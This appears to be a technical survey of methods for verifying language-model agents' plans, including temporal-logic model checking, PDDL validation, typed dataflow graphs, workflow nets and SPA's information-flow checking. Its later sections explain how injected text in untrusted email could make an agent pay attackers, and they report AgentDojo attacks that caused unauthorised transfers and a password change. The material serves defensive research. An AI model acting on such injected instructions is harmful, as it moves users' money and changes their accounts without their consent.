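The translator also writes the rule or goal in linear temporal logic, a notation for statements about how facts change over time. Here $F\,p$ means $p$ holds at some point in the run, and $G\,p$ means it holds throughout. Ramani and colleagues express a plan's goal as $F(\text{goal})$. For the invoice, a user might want the rule $G(\textit{paid} \rightarrow \textit{checked})$, which means that whenever the agent has paid, it has already checked the supplier.

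One method that NuSMV uses is to look for violations of a fixed length $k$. It builds the formula

$$\psi_k = \text{Init}(s_0) \wedge \bigwedge_{i=0}^{k-1} \text{Trans}(s_i, s_{i+1}) \wedge \neg\,\text{Rule}(s_0, \dots, s_k),$$

which holds if $s_0$ is a permitted starting state, each state leads to the next by a permitted move, and the run as a whole breaks the rule. A solver then searches for values of the variables that make the formula true. Any solution it finds describes a run of $k$ steps that breaks the rule. If there is no solution, no run of that length can break it.

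Ramani and colleagues tested the method on a simplified version of PlanBench, a set of artificial planning problems. The task was to decide whether a plan was valid. They compared the method with asking the same model directly for a verdict.

| Model | Method | No usable translation | Accuracy on the rest |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | Translation and model checker | 34.6% | 52.1% |
| GPT-4o | Direct verdict | – | 80.4% |
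| GPT-5 | Translation and model checker | 6.9% | 95.9% |
| GPT-5 | Direct verdict | – | 99.6% |

The direct verdict was more accurate for both models. The gap is wider than the table shows, because the accuracy figures leave out plans whose translation was unusable. If these count as failures, GPT-5 with the model checker reached the right verdict on about 89% of plans, and GPT-4o on about 34%.

Ramani and colleagues still favour the formal method because a direct verdict carries no guarantee. But the proof applies only to the formal translation, not to the original text. In the invoice example, the model checker can prove that the agent always checks the supplier before it pays, but not that the supplier passed the check, because the translator recorded *checked* and left out *approved*. Ramani and colleagues found real cases in which GPT-5's formal models passed verification without fully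 reflecting the plan's intended meaning.

*Planetarium* (Zuo, Piedrahita Velez and colleagues, 2024) measured such mistranslations directly and is the source of the low figures that Dantas and colleagues cite. The benchmark contains 145,918 pairs, each with an English description of a problem and a correct version in PDDL, the standard planning notation. The problems involve stacking blocks, carrying balls between rooms and painting floor tiles. Since one problem can have many correct translations, the researchers wrote an algorithm that compares the meanings of two versions. It turns each version into a graph of objects and facts, adds any facts that the goal implies, and tests whether the graphs match.

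In the paper's revised version of February 2025, 96.1% of GPT-4o's translations were valid PDDL and 94.4% described a problem that a planner could solve, but only 24.8% described the right problem. In about three out of four of the solvable cases, a planner would therefore have solved the wrong problem. The best model, a version of Google's Gemma 2 with extra training on the task, got the problem right 34.2% of the time.

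Not all of these errors were misunderstandings. The models often added object types that the problem did not use, apparently because similar problems online have them, and accuracy rose considerably when the test ignored these additions. Newer models probably also do better. GPT-5 clearly outperformed GPT-4o in the JPMorgan study, although that study scored only the final verdict, which can be right by luck when the translation is wrong. But Huang, Mohan and colleagues warn in *Language Model as Planner and Formalizer under Constraints* that the usual benchmarks describe only simple, generic environments and may overstate how well models plan. An office task is probably harder to translate than a block-stacking problem, because nobody has listed what each action requires and changes.

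Even if the translation is perfect, an executor that works from the prose may fill in details differently from the translator. Having the executor run the formal version avoids this problem, but then the formal version is the plan, and the proposer might as well have written it in the first place.

### Keywords inside prose

A less drastic approach is to keep the prose but fix its order and repetition. In RunAgent, the system that Srivastava and colleagues built, a plan consists of free-form steps with a few reserved keywords. IF makes a step conditional, GOTO jumps to another step, and FORALL repeats an instruction for every item in a list. The prefixes TOOL, PYTHON and LLM determine whether the system carries out a step with a tool, with freshly written code or with a language model. The invoice plan might look like this:

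```
1. TOOL: Find the unpaid invoices in the accounts inbox.
2. FORALL invoices found, check whether the supplier is
   approved and the amount is under $500.
3. IF no invoice passes both checks, GOTO 6.
4. FORALL invoices that pass, pay the supplier.
5. PYTHON: Add up the amounts paid.
6. Tell the user the total paid, or that nothing was due.
```

Srivastava and colleagues observed that a language model asked to do something for every item in a set usually does it for only some of them. The FORALL keyword addresses this by having the system carry out the instruction separately for each item.

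A checker can now read the order of the steps and the possible jumps from the plan, but the rest still depends on language models. One model determines which items a FORALL covers, and another determines whether the condition of an IF holds. The prefix TOOL ensures that some tool runs, but a model may choose which one. An IF combined with a backward GOTO also allows unbounded loops.

RunAgent adds checks during execution. At the start, a model derives a list of constraints from the task, each a single condition such as "no payment exceeds $500". After a step, one model call explains whether the step's output violates a relevant constraint, and a second call turns the explanation into a verdict. If the output fails, the system repeats the step with the error message attached. After a set number of failures, a fallback model performs the step, and the plan continues without further checks on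 that step.

On a set of calendar-scheduling problems, GPT-4o alone solved 58.3%, but only 46.9% when its prompt included a plan to follow. RunAgent, which also ran on GPT-4o, solved 81.1%, or 75.4% with constraint checking switched off. Most of the improvement therefore came from parts of the system other than constraint checking, such as carrying out the steps one at a time and running code. On trip planning, RunAgent solved only 14.7% of the problems, compared with 3.1% for GPT-4o alone.

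Solving these problems has no side effects, so RunAgent's error handling looks safer than it is. Its checks examine a step's output, so a check on step 4 would run after the agent had paid the supplier. Repeating the step could pay the supplier again, and the fallback would give the most troublesome payments the least checking.

### Tests for each subtask

In VeriMAP, the proposer writes tests along with the plan. Xu, Mitra and colleagues (2025), in *Verification-Aware Planning for Multi-Agent Systems*, describe how its proposer divides a task into subtasks, states which ones depend on which, and names the data that passes between them. For every subtask it also writes tests of the output, some in the programming language Python and some in prose. A subtask that selects the invoices to pay might come with these two:

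```
assert all(i["amount"] < 500 for i in to_pay)
assert len({i["number"] for i in to_pay}) == len(to_pay)
```

The first test fails if any selected invoice is for $500 or more, and the second fails if an invoice number appears twice. A prose test could have a language model decide whether each supplier's name matches an entry on the approved list. The output must pass every test before the next subtask begins. If it still fails after repeated attempts, the proposer writes a new plan and execution starts over.

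Such tests can prevent a wrong payment if the plan selects the invoices in one subtask and pays them in the next, because a failed test then stops the agent before it pays anything. But a proposer that misunderstands the task, for example by taking "approved" to mean "paid before", is likely to make the same mistake in the plan and in the tests.

Xu and colleagues compared the tests with a generic verifier, a language model that can use all the available tools but judges outputs only against the subtask's instruction.

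| Benchmark | Wrong results accepted: VeriMAP | Wrong results accepted: generic | Correct results rejected: VeriMAP | Correct results rejected: generic |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| HumanEval (short programs) | 2.1% | 13.5% | 18.6% | 0.7% |
| BigCodeBench-Hard (harder programs) | 23.0% | 71.6% | 21.6% | 0.0% |
| GSM8K (school maths) | 6.4% | 12.8% | 0.4% | 1.8% |
| Olympiads (competition maths) | 55.4% | 65.4% | 1.0% | 1.4% |
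| MultiHopRAG (questions about news) | 21.2% | 18.8% | 4.8% | 14.2% |

On the harder programs, 28.4% of the solutions from the system with the generic verifier were correct and 71.6% were wrongly accepted, which suggests that the verifier accepted every wrong solution. VeriMAP's tests caught many of the errors, but they also rejected many correct programs. On competition maths, most wrong answers passed both kinds of check, presumably because testing an answer to such a problem can be nearly as hard as finding it. On questions about news articles, where nearly all of VeriMAP's tests were in prose, VeriMAP accepted slightly more wrong answers than the generic verifier did. VeriMAP therefore caught more errors than the generic verifier only where the proposer could write most of the tests as code.

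### Lists, checklists, pseudocode and narrative

Writing plans in a more structured form might make an agent less able to do its task. *Does The Way You Plan Matter?* (Zambrano, Marjanović and colleagues, 2026) compares four ways of writing the same kind of plan: a numbered list of subgoals, a checklist of requirements, pseudocode (an informal imitation of a program) and a narrative. It uses 158 hard tasks from WebArena, chosen from 381 because an agent without a separate plan failed them in all 25 attempts, five with each of five models.

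The proposer wrote one plan per run after seeing the goal and a screenshot of the first page. The executor could then take up to 30 actions. With three models in each role, there were nine pairings, and each pairing tried every task five times with every format. The table shows the share of tasks that a pairing solved at least once in five attempts.

| Format | Average over nine pairings | Lowest | Highest | Pairings where it came first or tied |
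|---|---|---|---|---|
| List of subgoals | 6.0% | 2.5% | 10.7% | 4 |
| Checklist | 6.0% | 3.2% | 8.9% | 3 |
| Pseudocode | 5.1% | 3.2% | 8.2% | 1 |
| Narrative | 6.3% | 3.8% | 9.5% | 3 |

The averages differ by at most 1.2 percentage points, or about two tasks out of 158. The top-scoring format depended on the models. Checklists scored highest in all three pairings where Alibaba's Qwen 2.5 was the executor, and pseudocode did so only when Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash filled both roles. The ranking also depends on the measure. Subgoal lists have the highest score in the table, with GPT-4.1 mini as proposer and Gemini as executor, but that pairing succeeded in only about 5.0% of individual attempts, compared with about 5.5% for narratives with Gemini in both roles.

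Zambrano and colleagues probably give planning too much credit when they attribute every success on these tasks to it. Their reason is that the original agent, which had no separate plan, solved none of them. But the planning agents made nearly 200 attempts at each task across all formats and pairings, and the original agent might also have solved a few with that many tries.

None of the four formats is easier to check by itself. The executor in this experiment was a language model, which treated any IF or loop in the pseudocode as advice, just as it treated the narrative. Control structure in a plan becomes binding only when a program interprets it, as RunAgent does with its keywords.

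## Action sequences and dataflow graphs

PDDL, the planning notation into which language models so often mistranslate English, gives every action an exact meaning. A planning problem comes in two files, as *Frontier Large Language Models Rival State-of-the-Art Planners* (2025) explains with an example about delivering a package. The domain file defines the types of object and the actions. Each action has preconditions, which must hold before it runs, and effects, which are the facts it makes true or false. The problem file lists the objects, the facts that hold at the start and the goal. For the invoice task, the payment action might look like this:

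```
(:action pay
  :parameters (?i - invoice ?s - supplier)
  :precondition (and (from ?i ?s) (approved ?s)
                     (under-limit ?i) (unpaid ?i))
  :effect (and (paid ?i) (not (unpaid ?i))))
```

To check a plan, a validator simulates it. Let $s_0$ be the set of facts that hold at the start. Action $a_i$ can run only if $s_{i-1}$ contains all its preconditions, and it then produces the state

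$$s_i = (s_{i-1} \setminus \text{del}(a_i)) \cup \text{add}(a_i),$$

where $\text{del}$ and $\text{add}$ are the facts it makes false and true. The plan is valid if every action can run and the final state satisfies the goal. VAL, the standard validator, also identifies the first action whose preconditions fail, according to *Localizing and Correcting Errors for LLM-based Planners* (2026). Given a plan that pays invoice 118 twice, it would point to the second payment, because the first one removed the fact that the invoice was unpaid.

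A validator makes it possible to use an unreliable plan generator. *Frontier Large Language Models Rival State-of-the-Art Planners* ran every model-written plan through the validator VAL and discarded those that failed. This removed all invalid plans, but a model could still fail to find a valid plan when one existed. A plan is also valid only relative to the domain file. If the file omits the effect `(not (unpaid ?i))`, VAL will accept a plan that pays the same invoice twice.

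Preconditions can also enforce an order. If payment requires the fact `(signed-off ?i)` and only the approval action adds it, approval comes before payment in every valid plan. *LexiCon* (2025) automates this for more complicated rules by compiling them into the planning problem, so that an ordinary simulation checks them. When an action is not in the expected format, LexiCon's checker replaces it with the known action whose spelling is closest. That is reasonable for scoring a benchmark, but it would be dangerous in an agent that handles real money, because it could turn a garbled invoice number into the number of a different invoice.

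But a PDDL plan, like any fixed list of payments, cannot cover the invoices in an unread inbox, because the problem file has to name each one.

### From a list to a graph

A sequence also imposes an order that the task may not need. An agent with two invoices could look up both suppliers at once, but a list has to put one lookup first. A dataflow graph records only the dependencies. Its nodes are tool calls, and each edge carries a value of a stated type from the call that produces it to a call that uses it. This is the graph for one known invoice:

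```
read_email --Email--> extract --Invoice--> look_up_supplier
                         |                        |
                      Invoice                  Supplier
                         |                        |
                         +-------> check <--------+
                                     |
                                  Payment
                                     |
                                     v
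                                    pay --Receipt--> report
```

The tool `check` outputs a Payment only if the supplier is approved and the amount is under $500. If no other tool outputs a Payment and `pay` accepts only a Payment, then in any graph that passes a type check, `pay` must get its input from `check`. The executor can run a node only after all its inputs have arrived, so `pay` always runs after `check`, and the graph cannot pay an unchecked invoice.

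Without cycles, each node runs at most once, so a graph of $n$ nodes makes at most $n$ tool calls. This guarantees that the plan ends, but it also limits a graph with $p$ payment nodes to $p$ payments. If the inbox holds $p+1$ qualifying invoices, the agent leaves at least one unpaid, so no acyclic graph of this kind, fixed in advance, can handle every inbox.

The usual solution is a special "map" node, which contains a smaller graph and runs it once for each item in a list:

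```
find_unpaid --List of Invoice--> map [look_up, check, pay]
            --List of Receipt--> sum --Amount--> report
```

A map node works like the loop over a fixed collection in Girrens and Wang's plan language, so the checker needs to check the inner graph only once. If the inner graph turns an Invoice into a Receipt, the map turns a list of invoices into a list of receipts. An invoice that fails the check adds no receipt to the list.

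If the copies of the inner graph run in parallel, they can overwrite each other's results. *Automated Safety Analysis for Agentic Workflows* (Chen, Li et al., 2026) reports this bug in an example that NVIDIA ships with its NeMo Agent Toolkit. The parallel steps all wrote to one shared list, with no rule for merging their results. When two steps finished together, one result was lost or the program crashed. In the invoice task, the same bug could leave a payment out of the reported total.

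Language-model agents began to use such plans in 2023. In ReWOO, the proposer wrote all the tool calls before any of them ran, with placeholders such as "#E1" for their results. LLMCompiler had the model write a graph of function calls, mainly to save time and money by running independent calls in parallel. Later systems used the graph more for checking. SPIN (2026) has the model state each task's agent, dependencies and expected output in a fixed format. A validator checks the whole plan before execution and returns a list of errors, which the system can use to repair the plan.

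### Checking the graph

A checker can test a graph in four steps:

1. **Known nodes.** Every node must be a tool in the registry, the list of tools that the executor can call. A call to an invented tool such as `pay_all_bills` fails here.
2. **Matching types.** On every edge, the type of the output must match the type that the next node accepts. An edge from `extract` straight to `pay` fails, because it carries an Invoice and `pay` takes a Payment.
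3. **No cycles.** The checker removes a node that has no incoming edges, along with the edges that leave it, and repeats. If it can remove every node this way, the order of removal is also a valid order of execution. If some nodes remain and all of them have incoming edges, the graph contains a cycle.
4. **Reachable exits.** The checker searches forward from the start and backward from the exits. Any node that only the forward search finds is a trap, from which the plan can never finish.

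Each step takes time roughly proportional to the number of nodes and edges. The last step matters most in graphs with branches. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) describes an email agent whose developer adds a step to draft replies to normal-priority messages but forgets to connect it to the sending step, so the agent never sends those drafts. It still answers urgent messages, so a test that uses only urgent messages would miss the mistake.

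*PlanCompiler* (Harikumar, 2026) tests such checks on an agent's plans. GPT-4o-mini proposes a plan by choosing from 25 ready-made nodes, for tasks such as reading files, filtering tables and querying databases, and filling in their parameters. A validator then applies seven checks, including that every node is known, that types match and that the graph has no cycles, and rejects any plan that fails one. An accepted plan becomes a Python program assembled from code that a person wrote in advance.

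The benchmark had 300 data-processing tasks, and a system had to succeed in all three runs to pass a task. PlanCompiler passed 278. GPT-4.1 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, which wrote Python freely, passed 202 and 187. The model calls cost $0.36 in total for PlanCompiler, $2.14 for GPT-4.1 and $18.39 for Claude.

Part of this lead comes from the fit between the node library and the benchmark. In about 45% of its 98 failures, GPT-4.1 named a column of counts something other than the required "count". PlanCompiler's counting node always uses that name. Without these naming failures, GPT-4.1 would have passed roughly 246 tasks.

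The experiment also provides little evidence about graphs, because its plans were effectively lists. If the model's edges were malformed, incomplete or pointed backwards, the test program replaced them with a chain before validation, so a cycle could never reach the validator. Each node could take only one input, and each type of node could appear only once. The invoice graph above would fail, because `check` takes two inputs, and no plan could contain two payment nodes.

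In nine of PlanCompiler's 22 failures, the validator rejected the plan because of a type error, such as passing an open database connection to a node that expected a file path. The other 13 plans passed every check and ran without an error, but their output was wrong. The model had done the counting inside a database query instead of using the counting node, so the column had the wrong name. The validator treats a query as text and doesn't examine its contents, so it would also accept a filter for amounts under $5,000 when the user had asked for $500.

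### Ordering rules and the product construction

Type checks can enforce an order only where data flows from one step to the next. An approval may produce no data that the payment needs, so a rule such as "approval before payment" often requires a separate check. The usual method for this check applies to workflow graphs, which can contain cycles and in which an edge means that one step may follow another.

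The checker first turns the rule into a finite automaton, a state machine like the one Das and colleagues use. Suppose the rule is that each payment needs its own approval. The automaton starts in the state "none", meaning there is no unused approval. An approval moves it to "granted", and a payment then moves it back to "none". A payment in the state "none" moves it to "violated", where it stays.

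Now suppose the workflow graph has these edges:

```
start -> read       read -> approve     read -> report
approve -> pay      pay -> read         pay -> pay
```

The step `read` fetches the next invoice, and the edge from `pay` to itself retries a payment that timed out. The checker explores a graph called the product, in which each node pairs a step with the automaton's state after that step.

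| Current pair | Pairs that can follow |
|---|---|
| (start, none) | (read, none) |
| (read, none) | (approve, granted) and (report, none) |
| (approve, granted) | (pay, none) |
| (pay, none) | (read, none), which the checker has already visited, and (pay, violated) |

The search reaches a violation along the path start, read, approve, pay, pay. The retry pays again without a new approval, and if the first payment went through after all, the supplier gets the money twice. If the developer removes the retry edge, the search visits only five pairs and finds no violation.

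A simpler check would miss this error. It tests whether every path to `pay` includes a human step by deleting those steps from the graph and checking whether `pay` is still reachable. In this graph it isn't, so the graph passes even though one approval can lead to two payments.

With $|V|$ steps in the graph and $|Q|$ states in the automaton, the product has at most $|V| \cdot |Q|$ pairs, or 15 in this example. A graph with 5,000 steps and the same rule would have at most 15,000. A single automaton for ten such rules could need $3^{10} = 59{,}049$ states, so if the plan has to obey all ten, it is better to check them one at a time, as Das and colleagues did with their files. But the checker has to track both halves of a rule such as "every run either keeps a log or undergoes an audit" together, because some runs may satisfy one half and some the other.

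Xavier and colleagues built this method into Agentproof, a tool that extracts workflow graphs from four popular agent frameworks. They prove that if the product contains no violation, no run of the graph can break the rule as the automaton represents it. But the automaton may not match the intended rule. For example, one of their policies on approval for software deployments is `tool:deploy -> F tool:approve`. Its automaton reports a violation only if a second deployment occurs before an approval, so a workflow that deploys once and never calls `tool:approve` passes.

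The extracted graph can also be wrong. For one framework, Agentproof identifies human steps by looking for the word "human" in their names. It therefore classifies a step named "manager_approval" as a call to a language model even if a person makes the decision, and may raise a false alarm. It would presumably also classify an automated step named "humanize_reply" as a human step.

Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 workflows that they had written themselves, partly to include typical mistakes. Five (28%) had structural defects, such as dead ends or an exit that no path reached, and ten (56%) had no human approval step. These rates do not show how common such defects are in practice. The product construction found a missing review step that ten random test runs of the same workflow had not exposed.

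The structural checks, excluding the product, took about 105 milliseconds on an artificial graph with 5,000 steps. The product never exceeded 24 pairs in the tests.

The product includes every path in the graph, even those no run could take. Agentproof would therefore reject a plan that tests for $500 before the supplier lookup and again before the payment. The selective merging of Das and colleagues avoids this false alarm. Xavier and colleagues did not measure how often impossible paths cause false alarms.

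Chen and colleagues provide better evidence about real workflows. They collected 783 bugs from the public issue trackers of 13 frameworks, and only about a quarter were visible from the shape of the graph alone. They tested their own analyzer, APSIS, on 135 buggy workflows and the corrected versions. The frameworks' built-in validators caught none of the bugs. APSIS found half of them with structural patterns, and 84% when it also had information about how steps behave, such as which inputs they require and how they merge results that arrive together. It raised false alarms on 8% of the corrected workflows.

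Language models that judged the same workflows found 77% to 88% of the bugs, but they also flagged about half to two-thirds of the corrected versions. All the bugs in this test left some trace in the workflow's definition, so the detection rates do not cover mistakes that appear only at run time. APSIS also found 36 previously unknown bugs in public projects, and the maintainers had fixed 33 of them by publication.

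### When data determines the route

Engineers have long designed signal-processing software using dataflow graphs that run repeatedly on a stream of data. In synchronous dataflow, each node consumes and produces a fixed number of values every time it runs. UT Austin's *Introduction to Synchronous Dataflow* notes that such a graph can run forever in a fixed amount of memory. A checker can test in advance whether the numbers are consistent across the graph.

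Suppose `read` outputs three invoices each time it runs, `check` processes one at a time, and `report` summarises six. Let $q$ be the number of times each node runs in one cycle. Every node must consume exactly what the previous one produces, so

$$3\,q_{\text{read}} = q_{\text{check}}, \qquad q_{\text{check}} = 6\,q_{\text{report}}.$$

The smallest solution is two runs of `read`, six of `check` and one of `report`. If the developer adds an edge on which each run of `read` produces one value and each run of `report` consumes one, that edge requires $q_{\text{read}} = q_{\text{report}}$, which contradicts the other equations. Values would pile up on the edge without limit, so the checker rejects the graph.

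For larger graphs, the checker writes the equations as a matrix with one row per edge and one column per node. A connected graph of $n$ nodes has a solution exactly when this matrix has rank $n-1$. Lee and Messerschmitt published this test in 1987, and UT Austin's *Topology Matrices* describes it. A graph with cycles also needs enough initial values on those cycles to start running.

This calculation no longer works if the data determines where a value goes. Boolean dataflow adds a switch, which sends each value to one of two outputs depending on a true-or-false signal. For example, an invoice might go to `pay` if it passes a check and to `query` if it doesn't. If a later node needs one receipt from `pay` and one result from `query` each time it runs, and every invoice passes, the receipts accumulate without limit. Whether this happens depends on the invoices, which aren't available when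 the plan is checked.

A plan with switches is still decidable if its graph is acyclic and runs once, because the run always ends. Adding cycles and unlimited storage lets the graph repeat a calculation until some condition holds, which makes Boolean dataflow Turing-complete. Rice's theorem then applies, and *An Extended Survey and a Comparison Framework for Dataflow Models of Computation* (2025) notes that for such languages it is generally undecidable whether a graph can keep running without getting stuck.

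*PRUNE* (2018) restores decidability by letting nodes change their behaviour only within marked regions. The linked connections on both sides of a region must switch on and off together. For invoices, the signal that sends each one to `pay` or `query` could also determine which of the two results the next node collects. Each invoice then produces exactly one result, and nothing accumulates.

### Workflow nets

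Workflow nets, which companies have used since the 1990s to model business processes, show a similar boundary. A net consists of places, which hold tokens, and transitions, which remove tokens from some places and add them to others. A token in the starting place represents a new case, such as an invoice that has just arrived. Van der Aalst, van Hee and colleagues, in *Soundness of Workflow Nets*, define a net as sound if it meets three conditions:

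- From any state that a case can reach, it is still possible to finish.
- When the case finishes, no tokens remain elsewhere in the net.
- Every transition can occur in at least one run.

A common mistake is to join branches by a different rule from the one used to split them. Suppose each invoice goes either to a person or to an automatic check, but payment waits for both. The invoice never gets paid, so the net fails the first condition. Such errors are frequent even in professional models. Van der Aalst and colleagues cite a study of more than 2,000 process models, at least 10% of which had errors, and a set of 604 models from the software company SAP, 20.9% of which did. One SAP model was designed for a single application per vacant job and got stuck when a second arrived. An invoice workflow could fail the same way if one email contained two invoices.

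Another approach is to use a language in which some of these errors cannot occur. *Provable Coordination for LLM Agents via Message Sequence Charts* (2026) describes a language in which a model can write a workflow for several agents, and each agent's program is derived from it. The agents cannot deadlock, meaning they cannot all wait for one another, but this guarantee does not yet cover calls to a language model that never return.

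Soundness is decidable for ordinary workflow nets, although in the worst case the check needs memory exponential in the size of the net. It becomes undecidable when the language includes reset arcs, which empty a place no matter how many tokens it holds. Designers use reset arcs to model cancellation, such as dropping all pending work on an invoice the supplier has withdrawn.

Resets make it undecidable whether a net can finish with no tokens left over, because they let the net simulate a program with counters. The number of tokens in a place can represent a counter, but an ordinary net cannot test whether a place is empty. A net with resets can proceed as if the place were empty and reset it. An extra place keeps a running total of all the counters. If the counter was not actually zero, the reset destroys its tokens but leaves the total unchanged, so the total no longer matches the counters.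 At the end, the net removes tokens from the counters and the total in pairs, which leaves everything empty only if every counter treated as zero really was zero. Checking whether the net can finish empty therefore requires determining whether an arbitrary program stops.

A reset can also make a workflow that handles one case correctly fail when it handles several at once. *Soundness of reset workflow nets* (Blondin, Finkel and colleagues, 2024) gives a small net that always finishes correctly with one case. With two cases, a reset that belongs to one can remove the other's tokens, and only one case finishes. An agent that cancels one invoice might lose track of another in the same way.

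Blondin and colleagues also found an algorithm that gives a partial answer. It always terminates, and it correctly reports either that the net is sound for a single case or that it is unsound for some number of cases. But in the worst case, its running time grows faster than any function a LOOP program can compute.

Agent workflows can contain resets even if nobody intended to model cancellation. *Bounded Loops* (Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj, 2026) studies graphs in which a failed step can send work back to an earlier, completed step. This "repair" sets the count of used attempts back to zero, which has the same effect as a reset arc. Whether such a workflow ends is still decidable, but a user who knows that it ends does not thereby know how many attempts it will make.

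Bhardwaj and colleagues obtain a limit by capping the total number of repairs in the whole graph. If step $v$ may make $m_v$ attempts before a repair is needed, and the graph allows $R$ repairs, the total is at most

$$(R+1)\sum_v m_v.$$

A plan with four steps, three attempts per step and two repairs in total can make at most 36 attempts. Limiting repairs separately for each step would not bound the number of attempts, because two steps could keep sending work back to each other and restoring each other's allowance.

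## Restricted languages with branches and bounded loops

A dataflow graph needs a special map node to handle an inbox of unknown size. Some plan languages instead have branches and loops as ordinary steps, but limit them tightly enough that a checker can still cover every run in one pass. SPA, the plan-first agent built by Girrens and Wang, uses such a language.

### The six steps of SPA

An SPA plan is an ordered list of steps in JSON, a common text format for structured data. There are six kinds of step:

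| Step | What it does |
|---|---|
| `retrieve` | Loads a result stored during an earlier request |
| `tool` | Calls a tool and names the result; no other step can affect the outside world |
| `q-llm` | Has a quarantined model turn text into data of a stated shape |
| `display` | Shows text or results to the user |
| `condition` | Makes one comparison, then runs one of two lists of steps |
| `loop` | Runs a list of steps once for each item in a collection |

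The inputs of a step can be fixed values, earlier results, fields of earlier results, or lists and objects made up of these. A condition can test whether two values are equal, whether one is larger than the other, whether an item belongs to a collection, or whether a value exists.

Inputs cannot contain arithmetic, user-defined functions or templates (strings with gaps that the executor fills in), so every input shows directly which earlier results it uses. The ban on arithmetic isn't needed for this, since `a + b` also shows which results it uses, but it keeps the language small. Together with the limits on variables, it also prevents loops from performing the kind of calculation that makes LOOP programs hard to check.

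Conditions cannot contain "and" or "or". To express "A and B", the proposer puts the test for B inside the branch that runs when A holds. To express "A or B", it puts the test for B in the branch that runs when A fails, and must write the action twice. In return, the checker can find every decision that a step depends on by looking at the conditions and loops that enclose it.

A variable created inside a branch or a loop disappears when that block ends, so the checker needs to examine a loop body only once. A plan also cannot assign the same name twice along one path.

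### Labels and the flow rule

These restrictions make it easy to check where data flows. SPA labels every value with its confidentiality, or how secret it is, and its integrity, or how far its sources can be trusted. In the simplest version, confidentiality is either public or private, and integrity is either untrusted or trusted. An organisation can define more levels, and some may be incomparable, such as those for medical and financial secrets.

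When a value depends on two others, the checker combines their labels:

$$(c_1, i_1) \sqcup (c_2, i_2) = (c_1 \sqcup c_2,\; i_1 \sqcap i_2).$$

The result is at least as secret as the more secret input and no more trustworthy than the less trustworthy one. A table that mixes private payroll data with text from a public website is both private and untrusted.

Data may flow from a source $s$ to a destination $d$ only if

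$$C(s) \sqsubseteq C(d) \quad\text{and}\quad I(d) \sqsubseteq I(s),$$

where $\sqsubseteq$ means "is at most as high as". The destination must be cleared for data this secret, and the source must be at least as trustworthy as the destination requires. Each tool has an input policy that states both limits. It also has a minimum label for its output, because a mail search returns private, untrusted text even if its input was harmless.

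Data can also influence a step without being one of its inputs. In the plan "if the email contains the word 'yes', pay Acme $100", the recipient and the amount come from the trusted plan, but whoever wrote the email decides whether the payment happens. To track this, the checker keeps a program-counter label, $pc$, which records the secrecy and trustworthiness of the decisions that led to the current step. $pc$ starts as the label of the user's request. Inside a conditional, the checker combines it with the labels of the values compared, and inside a loop, with the label of the collection being looped over.

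The effective label of a step with inputs $x_1, \dots, x_n$ is then

$$\lambda_{\text{eff}} = pc \sqcup \lambda(x_1) \sqcup \dots \sqcup \lambda(x_n).$$

The checking algorithm goes through the plan in order and treats each kind of step as follows:

- **`retrieve`:** The result gets the label stored with it, combined with $pc$. If the label is missing, the checker rejects the plan.
- **`tool`:** The checker compares the effective label with the tool's input policy and rejects the whole plan if the flow rule fails. Otherwise the result gets the effective label combined with the tool's minimum output label.
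- **`q-llm`:** The result gets the effective label. A summary of an untrusted email is therefore untrusted too, so a quarantined model can't be used to launder an attacker's text.
- **`display`:** If the user may not see an item, the checker replaces it with a redaction marker and continues.
- **`condition`:** The checker updates $pc$ and checks both branches, since it cannot predict which one will run.
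- **`loop`:** The checker updates $pc$, gives the loop variable that label, and checks the body once.

### The invoice task in SPA

In a shorthand for the JSON, a plan for the invoice task could look like this:

```
1   tool        search_mail("unpaid invoice")          -> mail
2   q-llm       "List each unpaid invoice with its
                 supplier and amount." [mail]          -> found
3   tool        approved_suppliers()                   -> approved
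4   loop        inv in found.invoices
5     condition   inv.supplier in approved.names
6       condition   inv.amount lt 500
7         tool        pay(inv.supplier, inv.amount)    -> receipt
8   tool        payments_made("today")                 -> paid
9   q-llm       "Add up the amounts." [paid]           -> sum
10  display     "Total paid: ", sum.total
```

The loop cannot keep a running total, so the plan has to read the payments back from the bank, which adds steps 8 and 9.

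Girrens and Wang tell the proposer to use a quarantined model for simple sums if no tool can compute them. The model may add incorrectly, so a tool that returns the total would be safer. The plan above would also produce a figure that is too high if the user had made other payments that day.

The plan is well formed, but the flow check rejects it. Suppose that the user's request is public and trusted, and that `pay` accepts private data but requires trusted inputs. The labels are then:

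| Value or context | Confidentiality | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| $pc$ at the start | Public | Trusted |
| `mail` | Private | Untrusted |
| `found` | Private | Untrusted |
| `approved` | Private | Trusted |
| $pc$ inside the loop, and `inv` | Private | Untrusted |
| Effective label of `pay` | Private | Untrusted |

The check fails at step 7, so the executor never runs any of the plan, including the mail search.

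The supplier and the amount both come from emails, so the proposer might try to replace them with trusted values. If the trusted supplier table includes account numbers, it could write `pay(approved.acme.account, 120)` inside the loop. The checker would still reject the plan, even though both inputs are trusted, because the loop runs once for each invoice in untrusted mail. An attacker who sent three fake invoices could trigger three payments. Looping over the supplier table instead wouldn't help, since the plan would still have to test whether each supplier had sent an invoice.

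The organisation could change the policy so that `pay` accepts untrusted inputs. The plan would then pass, but so would a plan that took the account number from an email. SPA checks the combined label of all a tool's inputs, so it cannot require a trusted account number while accepting an untrusted amount. Girrens and Wang suggest setting separate requirements for each input as future work, along with adding endorsement, which raises a value's integrity after an explicit check.

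### What flow checking cost

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo with GPT-5.4 nano, a small OpenAI model, as both the proposer and the quarantined model. They ran the 97 user tasks without an attack and 949 cases with an attack.

| | Without flow checking | With flow checking |
|---|---|---|
| Task success without an attack | 53.0% | 29.0% |
| Attack success | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Runs that reached execution | About 81% | About 37% |
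| Runs stopped by the flow check | – | About 53% |

The task success rates give more weight to environments with more attack cases. With every task weighted equally, the agent completed about 51 of the 97 tasks without flow checking and 27 with it.

Flow checking lost those 24 tasks but stopped four attacks that succeeded without it. All four involved the same banking task, in which text from a quarantined model reached sensitive tools. Three led to unauthorised transfers and one to a changed password. The benefit looks small because fixing the plan in advance had already defeated almost every attack in the test. Flow checking matters more against an attacker who supplies a false account number without changing the plan, but these figures give little indication of how common such attacks would be.

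The loss was largest in the travel environment, at 35 percentage points, and smallest in banking, at about 6 points, or one task in 16. This is surprising because banking tasks often use outside data to make payments. The scoring may hide part of the loss. In another configuration, five banking tasks counted as successes even though the agent had not completed a plan, because the starting state already satisfied the test.

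A stronger model would probably complete more tasks, but the checker would still reject any correct plan for the invoice task.

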